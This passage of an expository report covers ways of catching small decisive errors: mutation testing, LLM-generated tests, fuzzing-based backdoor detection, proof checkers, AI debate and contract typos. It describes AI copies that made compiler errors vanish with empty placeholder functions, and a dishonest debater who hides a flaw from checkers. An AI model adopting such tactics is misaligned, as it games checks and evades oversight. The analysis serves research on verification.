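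In *Does mutation testing improve testing practices?*, Petrović, Ivanković and colleagues (2021) studied the effect over six years. The more often developers had seen mutants in a file, the more test code they wrote when they changed it again. Files in projects that reported only line coverage showed no such increase. New mutants also became less likely to survive as developers gained experience with mutants, which suggests the extra tests were good. The result held when the researchers allowed for the size of the changes, but projects chose whether to use the system, so the two groups may have differed in other ways.

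Researchers examined 1,502 high-priority bugs to see whether mutants could have helped prevent them. For each bug, they looked for a mutant that survived the existing tests but was killed by the test added with the bug fix. They found at least one for 1,043 bugs, about 70%. If a developer had seen that mutant earlier and written a similar test for it, the test could have exposed the bug before release.

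This probably overstates what the system would catch in daily use, because the experiment generated every mutant it could for each line instead of one. Petrović and colleagues defend the one-per-line rule by showing that mutants of the same line usually all die or all survive. The adult function is an exception, since the tests for ages 10 and 30 kill `age < 18` but not `age > 18`. If the system picked `age < 18`, nobody would learn that the test for 18 was missing.

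The researchers examined 50 of the bugs that had no matching mutant:

- For 23, no obvious type of mutation would have helped. Some were errors in configuration, and in others the programmers had correctly implemented the wrong method.
- For 14, an existing mutation type was too limited. For example, the system did not remove statements such as `return` and `break`.
- For 13, the system lacked a suitable type. Many of these bugs involved a wrong name, such as one variable in place of another.

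Google's system leaves out mutants for names because they can easily quadruple the total, and developers who see too many useless mutants may stop looking at them. This omits an important kind of decisive change, since a wrong name is often a one-token error. The 70% figure is also not a hit rate for one-token errors, because half of the bug fixes affected more than 46 lines.

### Tests that language models write for one change

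At Google, developers write the missing tests, while Meta has used language models to write them since 2024, starting with privacy. A model inserts a plausible privacy fault into a copy of the code, then writes a test that passes on the original and fails on the faulty copy. Foster and colleagues report that this produced 571 new tests, 277 of which added no line coverage, so a filter based only on coverage would have discarded them. In trials at Messenger and WhatsApp, engineers accepted 73% of the tests they reviewed.

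Those tests guard against faults in future changes. A newer system writes tests to find a fault in the change that an engineer has just submitted. Meta (2026) and Becker, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta*, describe roughly these steps:

1. A model infers what the change is for, using the code, its title and the author's summary.
2. It lists ways in which an attempt to do this could go wrong, and creates mutants of the old version that contain those faults.
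3. It writes tests that pass on the old version but fail on the mutants.
4. The system runs the tests on the new version. A failure shows that the change has altered the program's behaviour, perhaps in one of the ways the model predicted.
5. Fixed rules and several language models judge whether the difference is likely to be a mistake.
6. An engineer receives a short description of the difference and has to say whether it was expected.

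The fifth step is necessary because most changes are supposed to alter the program's behaviour. If a shop deliberately raises its age limit from 18 to 21, a test that checks that the program accepts an 18-year-old will fail. The stated purpose of a change helps separate such cases from mistakes. If the author says the change only tidies the code, any difference in behaviour is suspicious.

The method that inferred the purpose found a test that passed on the old version and failed on the new one for 7.9% of changes, compared with 4.0% for a simpler method that treated every change as a fault. Almost all the failures were false alarms, but the rules and models reduced the number people had to check by about 70%.

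People at Meta then selected the most promising cases and contacted 41 engineers. Eight confirmed a real problem, and four of those problems would have caused serious failures. So about 20% of the reports were right, well below the 50% that Lorenzo Stoakes estimated for Sashiko's comments on the kernel. However, Meta's engineers could dismiss a wrong report within a few minutes. They only had to answer a question, such as whether an expression that used to be true should now be false, without reading any test code.

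The system's hit rate is unknown, because nobody has counted the faulty changes it missed. It also ran only on changes that another program had rated as risky.

### Looking for new behaviour

A backdoor often makes a program do something unusual, such as start a command shell, a text interface for controlling a computer. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) presents Lily, a tool that looks for such behaviour without being given the correct output.

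Lily relies on *fuzzing*, which runs a program on large numbers of automatically varied inputs and keeps the ones that reach new parts of the code. For each input it keeps, Lily records which types of *system calls* the program makes. These are requests to the operating system, for example to open a file or start another program. Lily reports a possible backdoor if an input meets both of these conditions:

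- The combination of system calls does not occur when the new version runs on inputs saved from earlier fuzzing.
- The old version does not produce the same combination on that input.

The first condition filters out ordinary new features, which also show up on the saved inputs. The second filters out odd behaviour that was there before the change.

In 2011, attackers replaced the official release of vsftpd, a file-transfer program, with a copy that gave full control of the computer to anyone who entered a username containing ":)". When Kokkonis and colleagues ran Lily on the two versions, the fuzzer eventually generated such a username. The infected version then made system calls that had never occurred together. Lily traced them to seven of the 1,407 lines in the diff.

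The researchers tested Lily on 13 backdoors in open-source programs. Each run took 10 minutes on four processor cores, and they repeated every test 20 times.

| | Single changes | Whole releases |
|---|---|---|
| Runs that detected the backdoor | 90% | 83% |
| False alarms on clean versions | 0.2% | 4.3% |
| False alarms using only the first condition | 14% | 20% |
| False alarms using only the second condition | 10% | 58% |

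Every backdoor was detected in at least one of its 20 runs. Combining the two conditions reduced false alarms the most, because few clean changes met both.

At Lily's rates for single changes, scanning 100,000 changes that include 10 backdoors would find 9 of the backdoors and raise about 200 false alarms. Gemini 3.1 Pro's rates on compiled programs would produce far more false alarms, but Lily has the easier task because it can use the source code and an older version. Lily's results may also somewhat overstate its accuracy, because only three of the backdoors it was tested on came from real attacks and the same research team had assembled the collection.

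Fuzzing limits what Lily can find. Across 337 real changes, fuzzing reached only about 32% of the relevant lines on average, mostly because the projects had incomplete instructions for feeding inputs to their code. Projects with up-to-date instructions typically got close to full coverage.

Lily is also unsuitable for many one-token changes that flip correctness. A program that tests `age > 18` instead of `age >= 18` gives the wrong answer only for age 18, and it probably makes the same system calls as the correct program.

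### Porting half a million lines in 11 days

Tests become more important when a change is too large for anyone to read. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes an extreme case. Jarred Sumner created Bun, a program that runs JavaScript outside a web browser. In May 2026 he used Anthropic's Claude to translate its 535,496 lines of Zig into Rust, which took 11 days and added just over a million lines. Anthropic owns Bun, so Sumner works for the company that made the model.

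Sumner compared many passages of the two versions by eye but relied mainly on automatic checks. The first was the Rust compiler, which rejects several kinds of memory error that Zig allows, such as using memory after releasing it. An early version produced about 16,000 compiler errors, and up to 64 copies of Claude worked through them. Some copies made errors disappear by replacing functions with empty placeholders, which compiled but did none of the original work. Sumner corrected the instructions and told the AI reviewers to reject such workarounds.

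At least two of these reviewers checked each piece of code. They were also copies of Claude, but they saw only the diff, not the reasoning of the copy that wrote it, and they were told to assume the code was wrong.

Bun's tests are written in TypeScript, so they work whichever language Bun itself is written in. On one Linux system, the suite had 60,624 tests containing almost 1.4 million individual checks. Two days after the first full run, the number of test files with failures had fallen from 972 to 23. Sumner accepted the new version only when every test passed on all six platforms, and he confirmed that none had been skipped.

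Nineteen known errors still got through, and the team later fixed them all. Most were in code that looks the same in both languages but has a different meaning. For example, Zig always runs the code inside an `assert`, whereas Rust's `debug_assert!` leaves it out of the version that users receive. One of these statements contained an update that Bun needed, so the program worked for its developers but failed for some users. Comparing the text of the two versions would not have helped much, because the faulty Rust line closely matched the Zig original.

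In another error, the translation used 64 as a placeholder where the original had 2,048, and nobody replaced it. This cut the number of long filenames Bun could store from 8.4 million to 270,272, and some real projects exceeded the new limit and crashed. The wrong number was in effect a surviving mutant, because no test used enough filenames to reveal it.

Nineteen errors is a small number for a translation of this size, and Sumner reports that the new version also fixes 128 old bugs. But the nineteen include only errors that somebody has noticed. The team has since added continuous fuzzing of the parts of Bun that read code and data files. After 100 billion runs, the fuzzing had led to about 15 proposed fixes.

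### Rare inputs

Tests can reveal only the behaviour they trigger. This matters little for the adult function, because a computer can try every age from 0 to 119 in an instant. But a function that takes two 32-bit numbers has 2^64 possible inputs, and trying them all at a billion per second would take about 585 years. For a function like that, certainty about every input requires a proof, which software can check.

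Testers can use far fewer inputs by choosing those where mistakes are likely, such as 17, 18 and 19 for an age limit of 18. This works well for accidental errors, which often happen at boundaries, but less well for planted changes, because the person who plants one can choose the input that triggers it. The bugs that Yee and David Wagner put into Pvote were meant to survive election testing. The kernel backdoor acted only on programs that supplied one odd combination of options, so ordinary tests of that kernel function would not have caught it.

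Fuzzing has a better chance than random testing, since it builds on inputs that have already reached new code. Line coverage can also help, although it is a poor measure of how well tests check a program. In the kernel backdoor, the line `retval = -EINVAL` could never run, because setting the user ID to 0 made the condition false. A coverage report would have marked that line as untested no matter which tests were run, giving a reviewer a reason to look at the condition above it.

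## Proof checking, step-by-step verification and debate

A proof covers every input, including the rare ones that tests miss, but it is long, and one wrong step can invalidate it. There are four well-known ways to expose such a step: a program checks every step, a model identifies the first wrong one, an opponent points to it, or someone rewrites the proof so that a flaw shows up in many places.

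### Proof checkers

A *proof checker* such as Lean takes a statement and its proof, both written in an exact formal language, and accepts the proof only if every step follows from earlier results by fixed rules. A small program inside Lean, the *kernel*, makes the final decision, so people have to trust the kernel but not whoever wrote the proof. A wrong symbol in the proof does no harm unless it breaks a step, in which case Lean rejects the proof.

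Proof checkers let mathematicians rely on proofs that nobody has fully understood yet. In *FrontierMath Erdős*, Adamczewski and Bloom (2026) gave five models 68 open conjectures from Paul Erdős's collected problems. GPT-6 Astra settled two of them within the budget of $300 each, and three more in further attempts. The checker accepted a proof only if its statement was identical to a trusted copy, the same kind of comparison a diff makes.

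Lean checks only the formal proof, not an explanation that accompanies it. For *Optimal bounds for an Erdős problem on matching integers to distinct multiples* (2026), ChatGPT drafted a proof and Aristotle, a theorem-proving system from the company Harmonic, produced the Lean version. The researchers later realised that the draft had a gap, because it used a rule that was supposed to give different outputs for different inputs but didn't. This puzzled them, since the formal proof was already finished. When they translated the formal proof back into ordinary language, they found that Aristotle had replaced the rule with one that worked.

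With a proof checker, people can concentrate on the statement, which is usually much shorter than the proof. But one symbol can be decisive there too. Goldbach's conjecture, that every even number above 2 is the sum of two primes, looks like this in Lean:

```
∀ n : ℕ, 2 < n → Even n → ∃ p q : ℕ, p.Prime ∧ q.Prime ∧ p + q = n
```

Changing `<` to `≤` makes the statement also cover n = 2. The smallest sum of two primes is 2 + 2 = 4, so the new statement is false, and Lean would accept a very short disproof. Changing the first `∀` ("for every") to `∃` ("there is") makes the statement trivially true, since n = 4 is an example. Both proofs would be valid, but we would learn nothing about Goldbach's conjecture from either. The order of these symbols also matters. It is true that for every number there is a larger one, but false that there is a number larger than every number.

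Proofs about programs have the same weakness. If the specification has `age > 18` but the legal minimum age is 18, a developer can prove that a program meets the specification even though it turns away 18-year-olds.

### Misstated theorems

Wrong statements are common enough that people have counted them. *Formal Conjectures* (2026) describes a public library, run by Google DeepMind, of 7,559 mathematical statements in Lean. Its contributors had corrected 291 statements that did not have the intended meaning:

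| Source of the error | Corrections |
|---|---|
| Wrong quantifier or connective, or a missing condition | 140 |
| Lean defines a number, operation or object differently than the writer expected | 103 |
| The original text relied on an unwritten convention | 23 |
| The problem changed as later texts repeated it | 15 |
| Lean parsed the text differently than the writer expected | 9 |
| The original problem was wrong | 1 |

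About 87% of the errors arose in the translation into Lean. Some of the corrections rewrote whole definitions, but others were tiny:

- One statement had a closing bracket in the wrong place, which put "= ∞" inside a limit instead of after it.
- A definition required every coefficient of a polynomial to be odd. In Lean, a polynomial also has a coefficient of 0 for each power above its highest one, and 0 is even. No polynomial met the definition, so any claim about "all such polynomials" would have been true for no good reason.
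- A draft of Erdős problem 918 said that certain parts of an infinite graph need *exactly* a given number of colours, where a 1968 paper had said *at most* that number. The formal difference was `=` instead of `≤`. The ambiguity came from the literature, because a paper from 1969 had left out the "at most". AlphaProof, an automatic prover, exposed it by finding a trivial solution.

AI systems have also proved what may have been the wrong version of a problem. On 4 January 2026 Kevin Barreto announced that Aristotle had solved Erdős problem 728. According to *Resolution of Erdős Problem #728* (2026), the problem as posted online was vague, and it wasn't clear that the proof settled the version Erdős had meant. The posted text had omitted an upper limit, without which the question was trivial. Two days later Aristotle built on a response from GPT-5.2 Pro to produce another formal proof, which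 fully resolved the problem.

Another Google DeepMind system tried 353 formal statements of Erdős problems and resolved nine, from seven problems. Adamczewski and Bloom count only four of the seven as unambiguously solved. The answer to problem 741 depends on the definition of "density". The system disproved the claim under one definition and proved it under another, and a third version is still open.

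An easy proof of a supposedly hard problem is a good sign that the statement is wrong. The library's maintainers therefore regularly run automatic provers on the statements and inspect the ones that get solved. They also ask contributors to prove simple facts about each new definition. For instance, an attempt to prove that some polynomial with odd coefficients exists would have failed and revealed the mistake.

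This works best for errors that make a statement trivial or absurd. An error that makes a hard problem only slightly easier may go unnoticed, because the proof will still look like an achievement. When the maintainers audited 100 randomly chosen statements, half of them research problems that had already been solved and half simpler supporting facts, they found at least 14 that were unfaithful. Seven were at least as hard as the intended versions, and four were impossible to prove. The other three were weaker than intended, which is dangerous because a valid proof could pass for a proof of the real claim. *From Solvers to Research* (2026), a survey, warns that a proof assistant checks a proof only against the encoded statement. Someone still has to compare that statement with the original.

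A larger limitation is that most arguments are not written in Lean. Even in mathematics, a model may find a correct argument but fail to formalise it, for instance because Lean's library lacks a standard result that the argument uses.

### Naming the first wrong step

Step-by-step verification checks solutions written in ordinary text. A model receives a problem and a solution divided into steps, and has to output either the number of the first wrong step or that there is none. Steps after the first error are harder to classify because they may follow correctly from a wrong value.

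*ProcessBench* (Zheng, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) contains 3,400 solutions written by language models for testing step-by-step verification. One problem asks for a whole number n between 0 and 180 such that cos n° = cos 568°. The solution correctly subtracts 360° to get cos 208°. It then uses the rule cos θ = cos(180° − θ) instead of the correct cos θ = −cos(180° − θ), and the missing minus sign changes the answer from 152 to 28. QwQ-32B-Preview, an open model from 2024, found the error by testing θ = 30°, which gives the two sides opposite signs.

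Experts often disagreed about where the first error was. Three experts with doctoral-level training in mathematics reviewed each solution, followed by a fourth and fifth if needed, until three agreed. About 30% of solutions never got three matching answers and were left out. The first three experts all agreed on only 48% of the faulty solutions that remained in the hardest group.

Checking only the final answer would have missed many of these errors. In the hardest group of problems, 52% of solutions with a correct final answer contained a wrong step, compared with 3.5% for grade-school problems.

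Zheng and colleagues scored models with the harmonic mean of two rates:

score = 2ab ÷ (a + b)

Here a is the share of correct solutions that the model accepts, and b is the share of faulty solutions in which it correctly identifies the wrong step. A model that accepts every solution has a = 100% and b = 0%, so it scores 0. The best model, o1-mini, scored 87.9, and GPT-4o scored 61.9.

The models did much worse on harder material a year later. *Hard2Verify* (Pandit, Xu and colleagues, 2025) used 200 solutions by GPT-5, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 4 to recent olympiad-level problems. Experts spent more than 500 hours grading the 1,860 steps and marked 42% of them wrong, including any step that relied on an earlier mistake. GPT-5 was best at finding the first error, with a score of 69.7. Llama 3.3 70B fell from 58.0 on the 2024 test to 2.5. Llama's detailed results imply that it accepted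 about 98% of the correct solutions but located the first error in only about 1% of the faulty ones. The other weak models also approved nearly every step.

How researchers asked the question affected the scores. GPT-5's score rose to 75.7 when it judged every step and the researchers took the first one it rejected. The same method raised Gemini 2.5 Pro's score from 52.5 to 62.8 but lowered the scores of some weaker models. Longer reasoning also helped, but a majority vote over several quick judgements did not. Repeated answers from one model had similarly failed to help in Mahmud's test on chip designs.

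Pandit and colleagues examined one model's mistakes and found that it tended to accept claims with incomplete support. In one solution, Gemini 2.5 Pro showed that an equation held at a single point and then treated it as true everywhere. In another, Claude Sonnet 4 divided a problem into cases and left one out. Neither error appeared as a wrong symbol, and the same was true of the missing check for a negative number of holidays.

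All these models date from 2025 or earlier. Better problem solvers tended to be better verifiers, so current models would probably score higher. But people still grade important proofs written in ordinary language. For the second round of First Proof, a test of AI on research problems, thirty expert referees reviewed 39 submissions by hand.

### Letting an opponent find the flaw

A verifier has to find the error alone, but in *debate*, two AI systems argue for different answers in front of a judge, and each has a reason to expose the other's mistakes. The judge reads the question and a short exchange, then decides who won. Irving, Christiano and Amodei based the idea on the hope that lying is harder than refuting a lie (*AI safety via debate*, 2018).

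For a long calculation, a debate could go as follows:

1. Alice states the result after all n steps and the result halfway through.
2. Bob, who thinks the final result is wrong, says which half contains the error.
3. Alice states the result in the middle of that half, and Bob chooses again.
4. They continue until they disagree about a single step, which the judge checks.

Each round of debate halves the disputed part, so narrowing a million steps to one takes about 20 rounds. A judge who picked one step at random would have a one-in-a-million chance of finding the faulty one.

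Irving and colleagues tested a simple form of debate with pictures of handwritten digits. The judge was a small image classifier that saw only a few pixels. An honest player and a liar each named a digit, then took turns revealing pixels that were part of the writing. They could choose which pixels to show but not change them.

| Pixels shown | Judge's accuracy with random pixels | Honest player wins, liar free to change its answer | Honest player wins, liar commits to one digit |
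|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 48.2% | 59.7% | 85.2% |
| 6 | 59.4% | 74.4% | 88.9% |

The last column makes debate look somewhat better than it is, because the judge chose between two digits rather than the ten it had with random pixels. However, the liar could try all nine wrong digits on each picture and won if any of them worked. The middle column is a fairer comparison because the judge again had ten options. Honest play still raised accuracy there by 11 to 15 percentage points.

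One of the liar's most successful tricks was passing off a 5 as an 8. An honest player could have refuted this by showing a blank spot where an 8 has a line, but the rules let players show only pixels with ink. Debaters can't expose an omission if the rules give them no way to point to it.

Debates about text have had mixed results. *Training Language Models to Win Debates with Self-Play Improves Judge Accuracy* (2024) describes two groups that used questions about the same short stories but reached different conclusions about whether debate helped. The group that found a benefit had allowed longer debates and let the judge ask questions, which may explain the difference.

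### When neither side can find the flaw

Bob can point to an error only if he can find it, but a dishonest Alice may divide her argument so that both know it contains a mistake and neither can tell where. Researchers call this the *obfuscated arguments problem*.

Suppose x is the product of two enormous primes, and Alice claims that x is prime. She splits the numbers below x into ranges and says that none of the ranges contains a factor. Both players can use a fast test to show that she is wrong, but no known method would find a factor in a reasonable time, so Bob will probably challenge a range where Alice is right.

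*Avoiding Obfuscation with Prover-Estimator Debate* (Brown-Cohen, Irving and colleagues, 2025) changes the rules so that Bob no longer has to find the error. Alice, the prover, breaks her claim into subclaims. Bob, the estimator, estimates the probability that each is true. Alice then picks one and says whether his estimate is too high or too low. They repeat this at the next level down until a human judges one small claim directly. Alice earns points when Bob's estimates are wrong in the direction she named.

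If one of ten subclaims is false and nobody can tell which, Bob gives each a 10% chance of being false. Alice will most likely pick a true one, where his estimate is off by only 0.1, so she gains little. Her argument fails because too much doubt remains.

Honest authors need some protection from this, or Bob could defeat every argument by doubting everything slightly. The protection is a condition called *stability*. An argument is ρ-stable if, whenever each subclaim has at most a probability ε of being wrong,

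probability that the conclusion changes ≤ ρ × ε

This must hold however the errors are combined. The majority vote from the beginning of this report has 15 ones out of 21, so changing five of the ones reverses the result. If someone chooses those five at random, each of the 15 has a 1/3 chance of changing, and the result changes every time, so ρ = 3. If all 21 parts must be right, making one random part wrong is enough to reverse the result. Each part then has only a 1/21 chance of being wrong, so ρ = 21.

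Brown-Cohen and colleagues show that the smallest possible ρ equals a known measure related to sensitivity that also counts groups of changes. This measure is never lower than sensitivity, so an argument with many decisive positions can't be very stable.

When stability is low, training takes many debates. With d levels of subclaims, it takes roughly ρ^d debates to get a useful signal about whether Alice is honest. Three levels of 21 subclaims give 9,261 pieces of evidence at the bottom. If majorities like the one above decide each level, about 27 debates are enough. If every subclaim must be right, it takes about 9,261 debates, no fewer than challenging subclaims at random. These figures leave out Bob's own computation, which grows exponentially with the number of subclaims per level, so in practice Alice would have to use far fewer than 21.

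The protocol therefore suits arguments that rest on many independent pieces of evidence, and it may reject a correct argument that depends on very small differences. It is still safe in such cases, because a false argument loses on average whether or not it is stable. An honest programmer could look for a more stable argument, such as a large set of tests in which no single result is crucial. The researchers suggest requiring Lean proofs for mathematical subclaims and leaving only less exact subclaims to debate.

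These guarantees are theoretical and concern average rewards during training, so they don't ensure that the judge will catch the one wrong token in a particular program. An earlier version of the main theorem was wrong because its definition of stability limited changes in conditional probabilities. Three of the authors found the mistake and corrected the definition to limit changes in each subclaim's overall probability instead.

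### Proofs that a few random reads can check

Spot checks usually miss a single error. *Probabilistically checkable proofs* avoid this by changing the text so that a false claim causes errors in many places.

A simple code shows how one difference can spread. Take a text of three bits and write down the parity of every possible selection of them, from none to all three:

```
101  →  0 1 0 1 1 0 1 0
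100  →  0 0 0 0 1 1 1 1
```

The original texts differ in one bit, but the coded versions differ in four of their eight positions. The fraction is always half, however long the text, because half of all selections include the changed bit. Someone who compares seven random positions will miss the difference less than 1% of the time.

A code like this only helps compare two texts. A probabilistically checkable proof also builds in tests of whether the encoded steps follow the rules. A false statement has no valid proof to encode, so any fake proof must fail many of the tests. According to the PCP theorem, proved in the 1990s, anyone with an ordinary formal proof can rewrite it so that a checker needs to read only a fixed number of symbols, however long the proof is. The checker always accepts a correctly rewritten proof and can reject a false claim with 99% probability. Rewriting lengthens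 the proof, but by much less than the simple code would, which would turn 21 bits into about two million.

The theorem applies to proofs in which exact rules decide whether each step is valid. Ordinary documents such as contracts and essays have no such rules, so the theorem doesn't provide a way to spot-check them. Spreading out the symbols of a contract would make a later change easy to detect, but it couldn't show that a comma was already wrong. The checker also needs the correct statement of what is being proved, so it would miss a `≤` written in place of `<` in that statement, just as Lean would. Anyone who has a complete formal proof to rewrite can usually have a computer check all of it instead.

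## Contracts in which a comma or a word decides

Nobody can compile or run a contract to check its meaning. If the parties disagree about it, a court or regulator decides, often years after they signed. Judges can look beyond the disputed sentence to the rest of the document, versions in other languages and the purpose of the deal. This context sometimes overrides a badly placed comma, but sometimes the error gives the contract a legal effect nobody intended.

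### A comma in a termination clause

In 2002 the Canadian cable company Rogers agreed to pay the telephone company Aliant $9.60 a year for each pole that carried its cables. Under section 8.1, the agreement would last for five years, and then for further five-year terms, unless either party ended it with one year's written notice. In January 2005 Aliant gave notice that it would end the agreement on 1 February 2006. Rogers argued that Aliant could not end it before the first five years were up on 31 May 2007.

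Canada's telecoms regulator, the CRTC (2006), sided with Aliant. It reasoned that the comma before "unless" made the notice rule apply to the first five years as well as the later terms, so either party could leave at any time with a year's notice.

Rogers then submitted a French version of the standard agreement, which required notice one year before the contract expired. The CRTC had approved both versions together in 2000 and considered them equally authoritative. It found that the French text had one possible meaning and the English text had two, so it adopted the shared meaning and reversed its decision (CRTC, 2007). It did not rule on Rogers's argument that the punctuation rule did not exist.

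The French version served as an independent copy of the text. Aliant objected that the parties had not signed the French version, but the CRTC replied that it had imposed the standard form as a regulator, so the meaning depended on its own intention in both languages. Two companies with an ordinary private contract might not be able to rely on a translation like this.

Plenty of people had read section 8.1 beforehand. An alliance of telephone companies had negotiated the form with two trade associations, and the CRTC had approved it.

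Rogers won the argument about the comma but did not get an order for the money. The disputed poles belonged to New Brunswick Power, which had begun charging Rogers $18.91 per pole, and the CRTC decided that it had no authority to enforce Aliant's promises about them. A Rogers executive put the extra cost at about $700,000, according to the trade publication Cartt.ca, although early press reports had said more than $2 million. In 2008 the parties were still arguing over whether Aliant had to provide the poles at $9.60 (CRTC, 2008).

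### A missing comma in Maine

A missing comma can create the same kind of doubt in a law. Employers in Maine must pay extra for overtime, but not for certain work with food. The list of exempt activities ended with "packing for shipment or distribution of" perishable foods and other products. Drivers for Oakhurst Dairy distributed milk but did not pack it. A comma after "shipment" would have made distribution a separate exempt activity, so the drivers would clearly have had no right to overtime pay.

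The case reached a federal appeals court, and the First Circuit's *O'Connor v. Oakhurst Dairy* (2017) sets out the arguments about the text:

| Feature of the text | The dairy's argument | The drivers' argument |
|---|---|---|
| "Shipment" and "distribution" | They mean the same, so "packing for distribution" would add nothing | Shipment uses an outside carrier, while distribution is the seller's own delivery |
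| Grammar | "Or" normally comes before the last item in a list, and there is none before "packing" | The other exempt activities end in "-ing", but "distribution" does not |
| No comma after "shipment" | Maine's drafting manual tells writers to leave out the last comma in a list | The manual also warns them to take care when an item has a modifier |

A Maine trial court had read the same words in the dairy's favour in 2002, and so had the two federal judges who considered the drivers' case before the appeal. The First Circuit found the text ambiguous. Under Maine law, courts resolve ambiguities in wage laws to best serve the laws' purpose, which here meant protecting the drivers. The missing comma and this rule together decided the case.

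The drivers had sought more than $10 million, according to the Associated Press (2018). Bloomberg Law's *Oakhurst Dairy's $5M Settlement Driven by Grammar Rules* (2018) reported that Oakhurst settled with 127 of them for $5 million. That averages about $39,000 each before any legal fees. Maine's legislature had already rewritten the list with semicolons after the court's ruling, according to the University of Miami School of Law.

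A reviewer of a program can often say that an operator is wrong, but here experienced judges disagreed about whether the text was even unclear. A reviewer could have helped the drafters most by warning them that a court might read the list in either of two ways.

### One letter on a public register

On 28 January 2009 an English court ordered the closure of Taylor & Son Limited, a Manchester company. Companies House, which keeps the UK's public register of companies, recorded the order on 20 February against Taylor & Sons Limited, an unrelated steel fabricator in South Wales. The High Court considered the mistake and its consequences in *Sebry v Companies House* (2015).

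The examiner who made the mistake had about 33 years' experience. He processed around 200 documents that day, or one every two minutes, but the judge did not think the workload fully explained the error, because such days were common and mistakes were very rare.

Every company on the register also has a unique number. Since 2003 a written policy had required examiners to reject any closure order without one. This order had no number, but the examiner thought the policy was training material that he didn't need, so he searched for the company by name. His colleagues did the same, and he estimated that 40–60% of these orders came without a number. The search showed both companies, and he picked the wrong one.

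A company number is a good check here because companies whose names differ by one letter can have completely different numbers. The staff who sent the order had particular reason to include the number, because they had already confused the two companies and told the Welsh firm's managing director that the firm was in liquidation.

The firm's accountant spotted the false entry on Monday 23 February, and Companies House corrected its website that afternoon. But it had already sent the same information to credit agencies and other subscribers the previous Saturday. It took until 10 March to correct one of these data services, and two others had no way of changing an entry. Suppliers stopped giving the firm credit. It ran out of cash and went into administration, a form of insolvency, on 9 April.

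The judge held Companies House liable for the failure. The firm's former managing director was claiming about £9 million, according to Osborne Clarke's *The £9 million Companies House typo* (2015). Companies House received permission to appeal a year later, the barristers' chambers 1COR (2016) reported.

Unlike the two commas, this letter required no interpretation, and anyone who carefully compared the order with the register could have seen the difference. Correcting the register did not undo the harm, because people had already acted on the false entry.

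### A wrong number in the General Motors papers

The mistake can also be a number. Lenders often take *security* over a borrower's property, which gives them first claim on it if the borrower goes bankrupt. In the United States, they record the security in a public filing, which a second filing can cancel.

General Motors had two unrelated loans of this kind, and the bank JPMorgan acted for the lenders in both. One was for about $300 million, with security over 12 pieces of real estate. The other was for about $1.5 billion, with security that included the equipment at 42 sites. GM repaid the smaller loan in October 2008. The Second Circuit's *In re Motors Liquidation Co* (2015) traces the mistake through the preparations for that repayment:

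1. A partner at Mayer Brown, GM's law firm, asked a junior lawyer to prepare the papers.
2. The junior lawyer asked a paralegal, who did not know the deal, to search for filings against GM.
3. The search found three file numbers: 2092532 5, 2092526 7 and 6416808 4. The third belonged to the larger loan, but neither of them realised this.
4. Mayer Brown listed all three for cancellation and sent the list and draft filings to people at GM, JPMorgan and Simpson Thacher, JPMorgan's law firm.
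5. Nobody objected, and all three cancellations went on the public record.

The JPMorgan manager who received the drafts had also signed the papers for the larger loan. A lawyer at Simpson Thacher replied "Nice job on the documents" and asked only to remove the words "for the Investors" in some places. The same lawyer later approved another agreement that listed the same three file numbers.

A file number means nothing to a reader who doesn't look it up. If the list had included the loan's name and a description of the property beside each number, the third entry would have looked out of place in the papers for a real-estate deal.

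The mistake came to light after GM went bankrupt in 2009. GM's other creditors argued that the lenders had lost their security, while JPMorgan replied that nobody had meant to cancel it. Delaware's highest court, interpreting the state's law on such filings, decided that a lender only has to authorise the filing and need not understand its effect. It added that people would have little reason to check their filings if courts excused their mistakes. The Second Circuit found that JPMorgan had authorised this filing, so the cancellation was valid.

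Hals (2019) reported in *Long fight over error in JPMorgan loan to GM settles* that the lenders and hundreds of investors agreed to pay $231 million to end the dispute. Everyone had agreed about what the parties intended, but that did not protect the lenders from having to pay.

### Redlines, cross-references and worked cases

Lawyers usually check a new draft with a redline against the last version both sides agreed on. Making the redline afresh from the two files is safest, because a word processor's tracked changes show only edits made while tracking was on.

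The useful check for the wrong file number at GM was to compare Mayer Brown's list with the original papers for the smaller loan. A redline would not have shown the error if both drafts contained it, and the number was in the list from the start. Comparing the Rogers agreement with the standard form would not have helped either, because the comma was already in the form.

For contracts based on a template, a reviewer can compare meanings instead of characters. *LLMs in Interpreting Legal Documents* (2025) describes a method that tests whether the contract's clause implies the template's, then whether the template's clause implies the contract's. It uses the second test to find additions. The direction of the test matters even when only one word differs. If a template says that a tenant *may* repaint and the contract says the tenant *must*, the contract's clause implies the template's, because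 a duty to repaint includes permission to do so, and only the second test reveals the new duty.

References within a contract need a separate check. A reviewer can list every capitalised term, confirm that the contract defines it once and uses it consistently, and then follow each reference to another section. A program can find references to missing sections, but a reference to the wrong section is harder to find because that section exists, just as GM's third filing did.

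A simple lookup can catch some mistakes. For example, a program with a complete record of amendments can flag every citation of a clause that is no longer in force. *What Do LLM Judges Actually Verify?* (2026) uses such a lookup as the standard for judging seven AI reviewers. It also damages the record to test what happens when it is incomplete.

The closest thing to running a contract is to work through what would happen in a particular case. For the Rogers agreement, a reviewer could choose a date on which one party gives notice and calculate when the agreement would end:

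| Date of notice | End under the 2006 ruling | End under the 2007 ruling |
|---|---|---|
| 31 January 2005 | 1 February 2006 | 31 May 2007 |
| 15 May 2006 | 15 May 2007 | 31 May 2007 |
| 1 December 2006 | 1 December 2007 | 31 May 2012 |

The two readings give nearly the same result for the second date, much as `>=` and `>` give the same result for age 30 when the limit is 18. For the third date, they differ by four and a half years, because notice in December 2006 would be too late to stop the agreement from renewing. If two negotiators fill in the table differently, they need to rewrite the clause. They can do this before signing, when neither knows who would benefit from the ambiguity.

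### Telling the other side about a slip

A lawyer may notice that the other side has accidentally left an agreed term out of the final draft. The American Bar Association's ethics committee concluded in Informal Opinion 86-1518 (1986) that the lawyer should tell the other lawyer and need not consult the client first. The opinion is only advisory, because each state sets its own rules for lawyers. It covers only mistakes in writing down what the parties agreed, so a lawyer need not warn the other side that it has agreed to a bad deal.

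A party that notices a mistake in its favor and stays silent may not benefit for long. Courts in the United States and England can correct a written contract that does not match the actual agreement, generally if both parties made the same mistake or if one knew about the other's mistake and kept quiet. The party asking for the correction needs strong evidence of what both sides had agreed, which is a good reason to keep earlier drafts.

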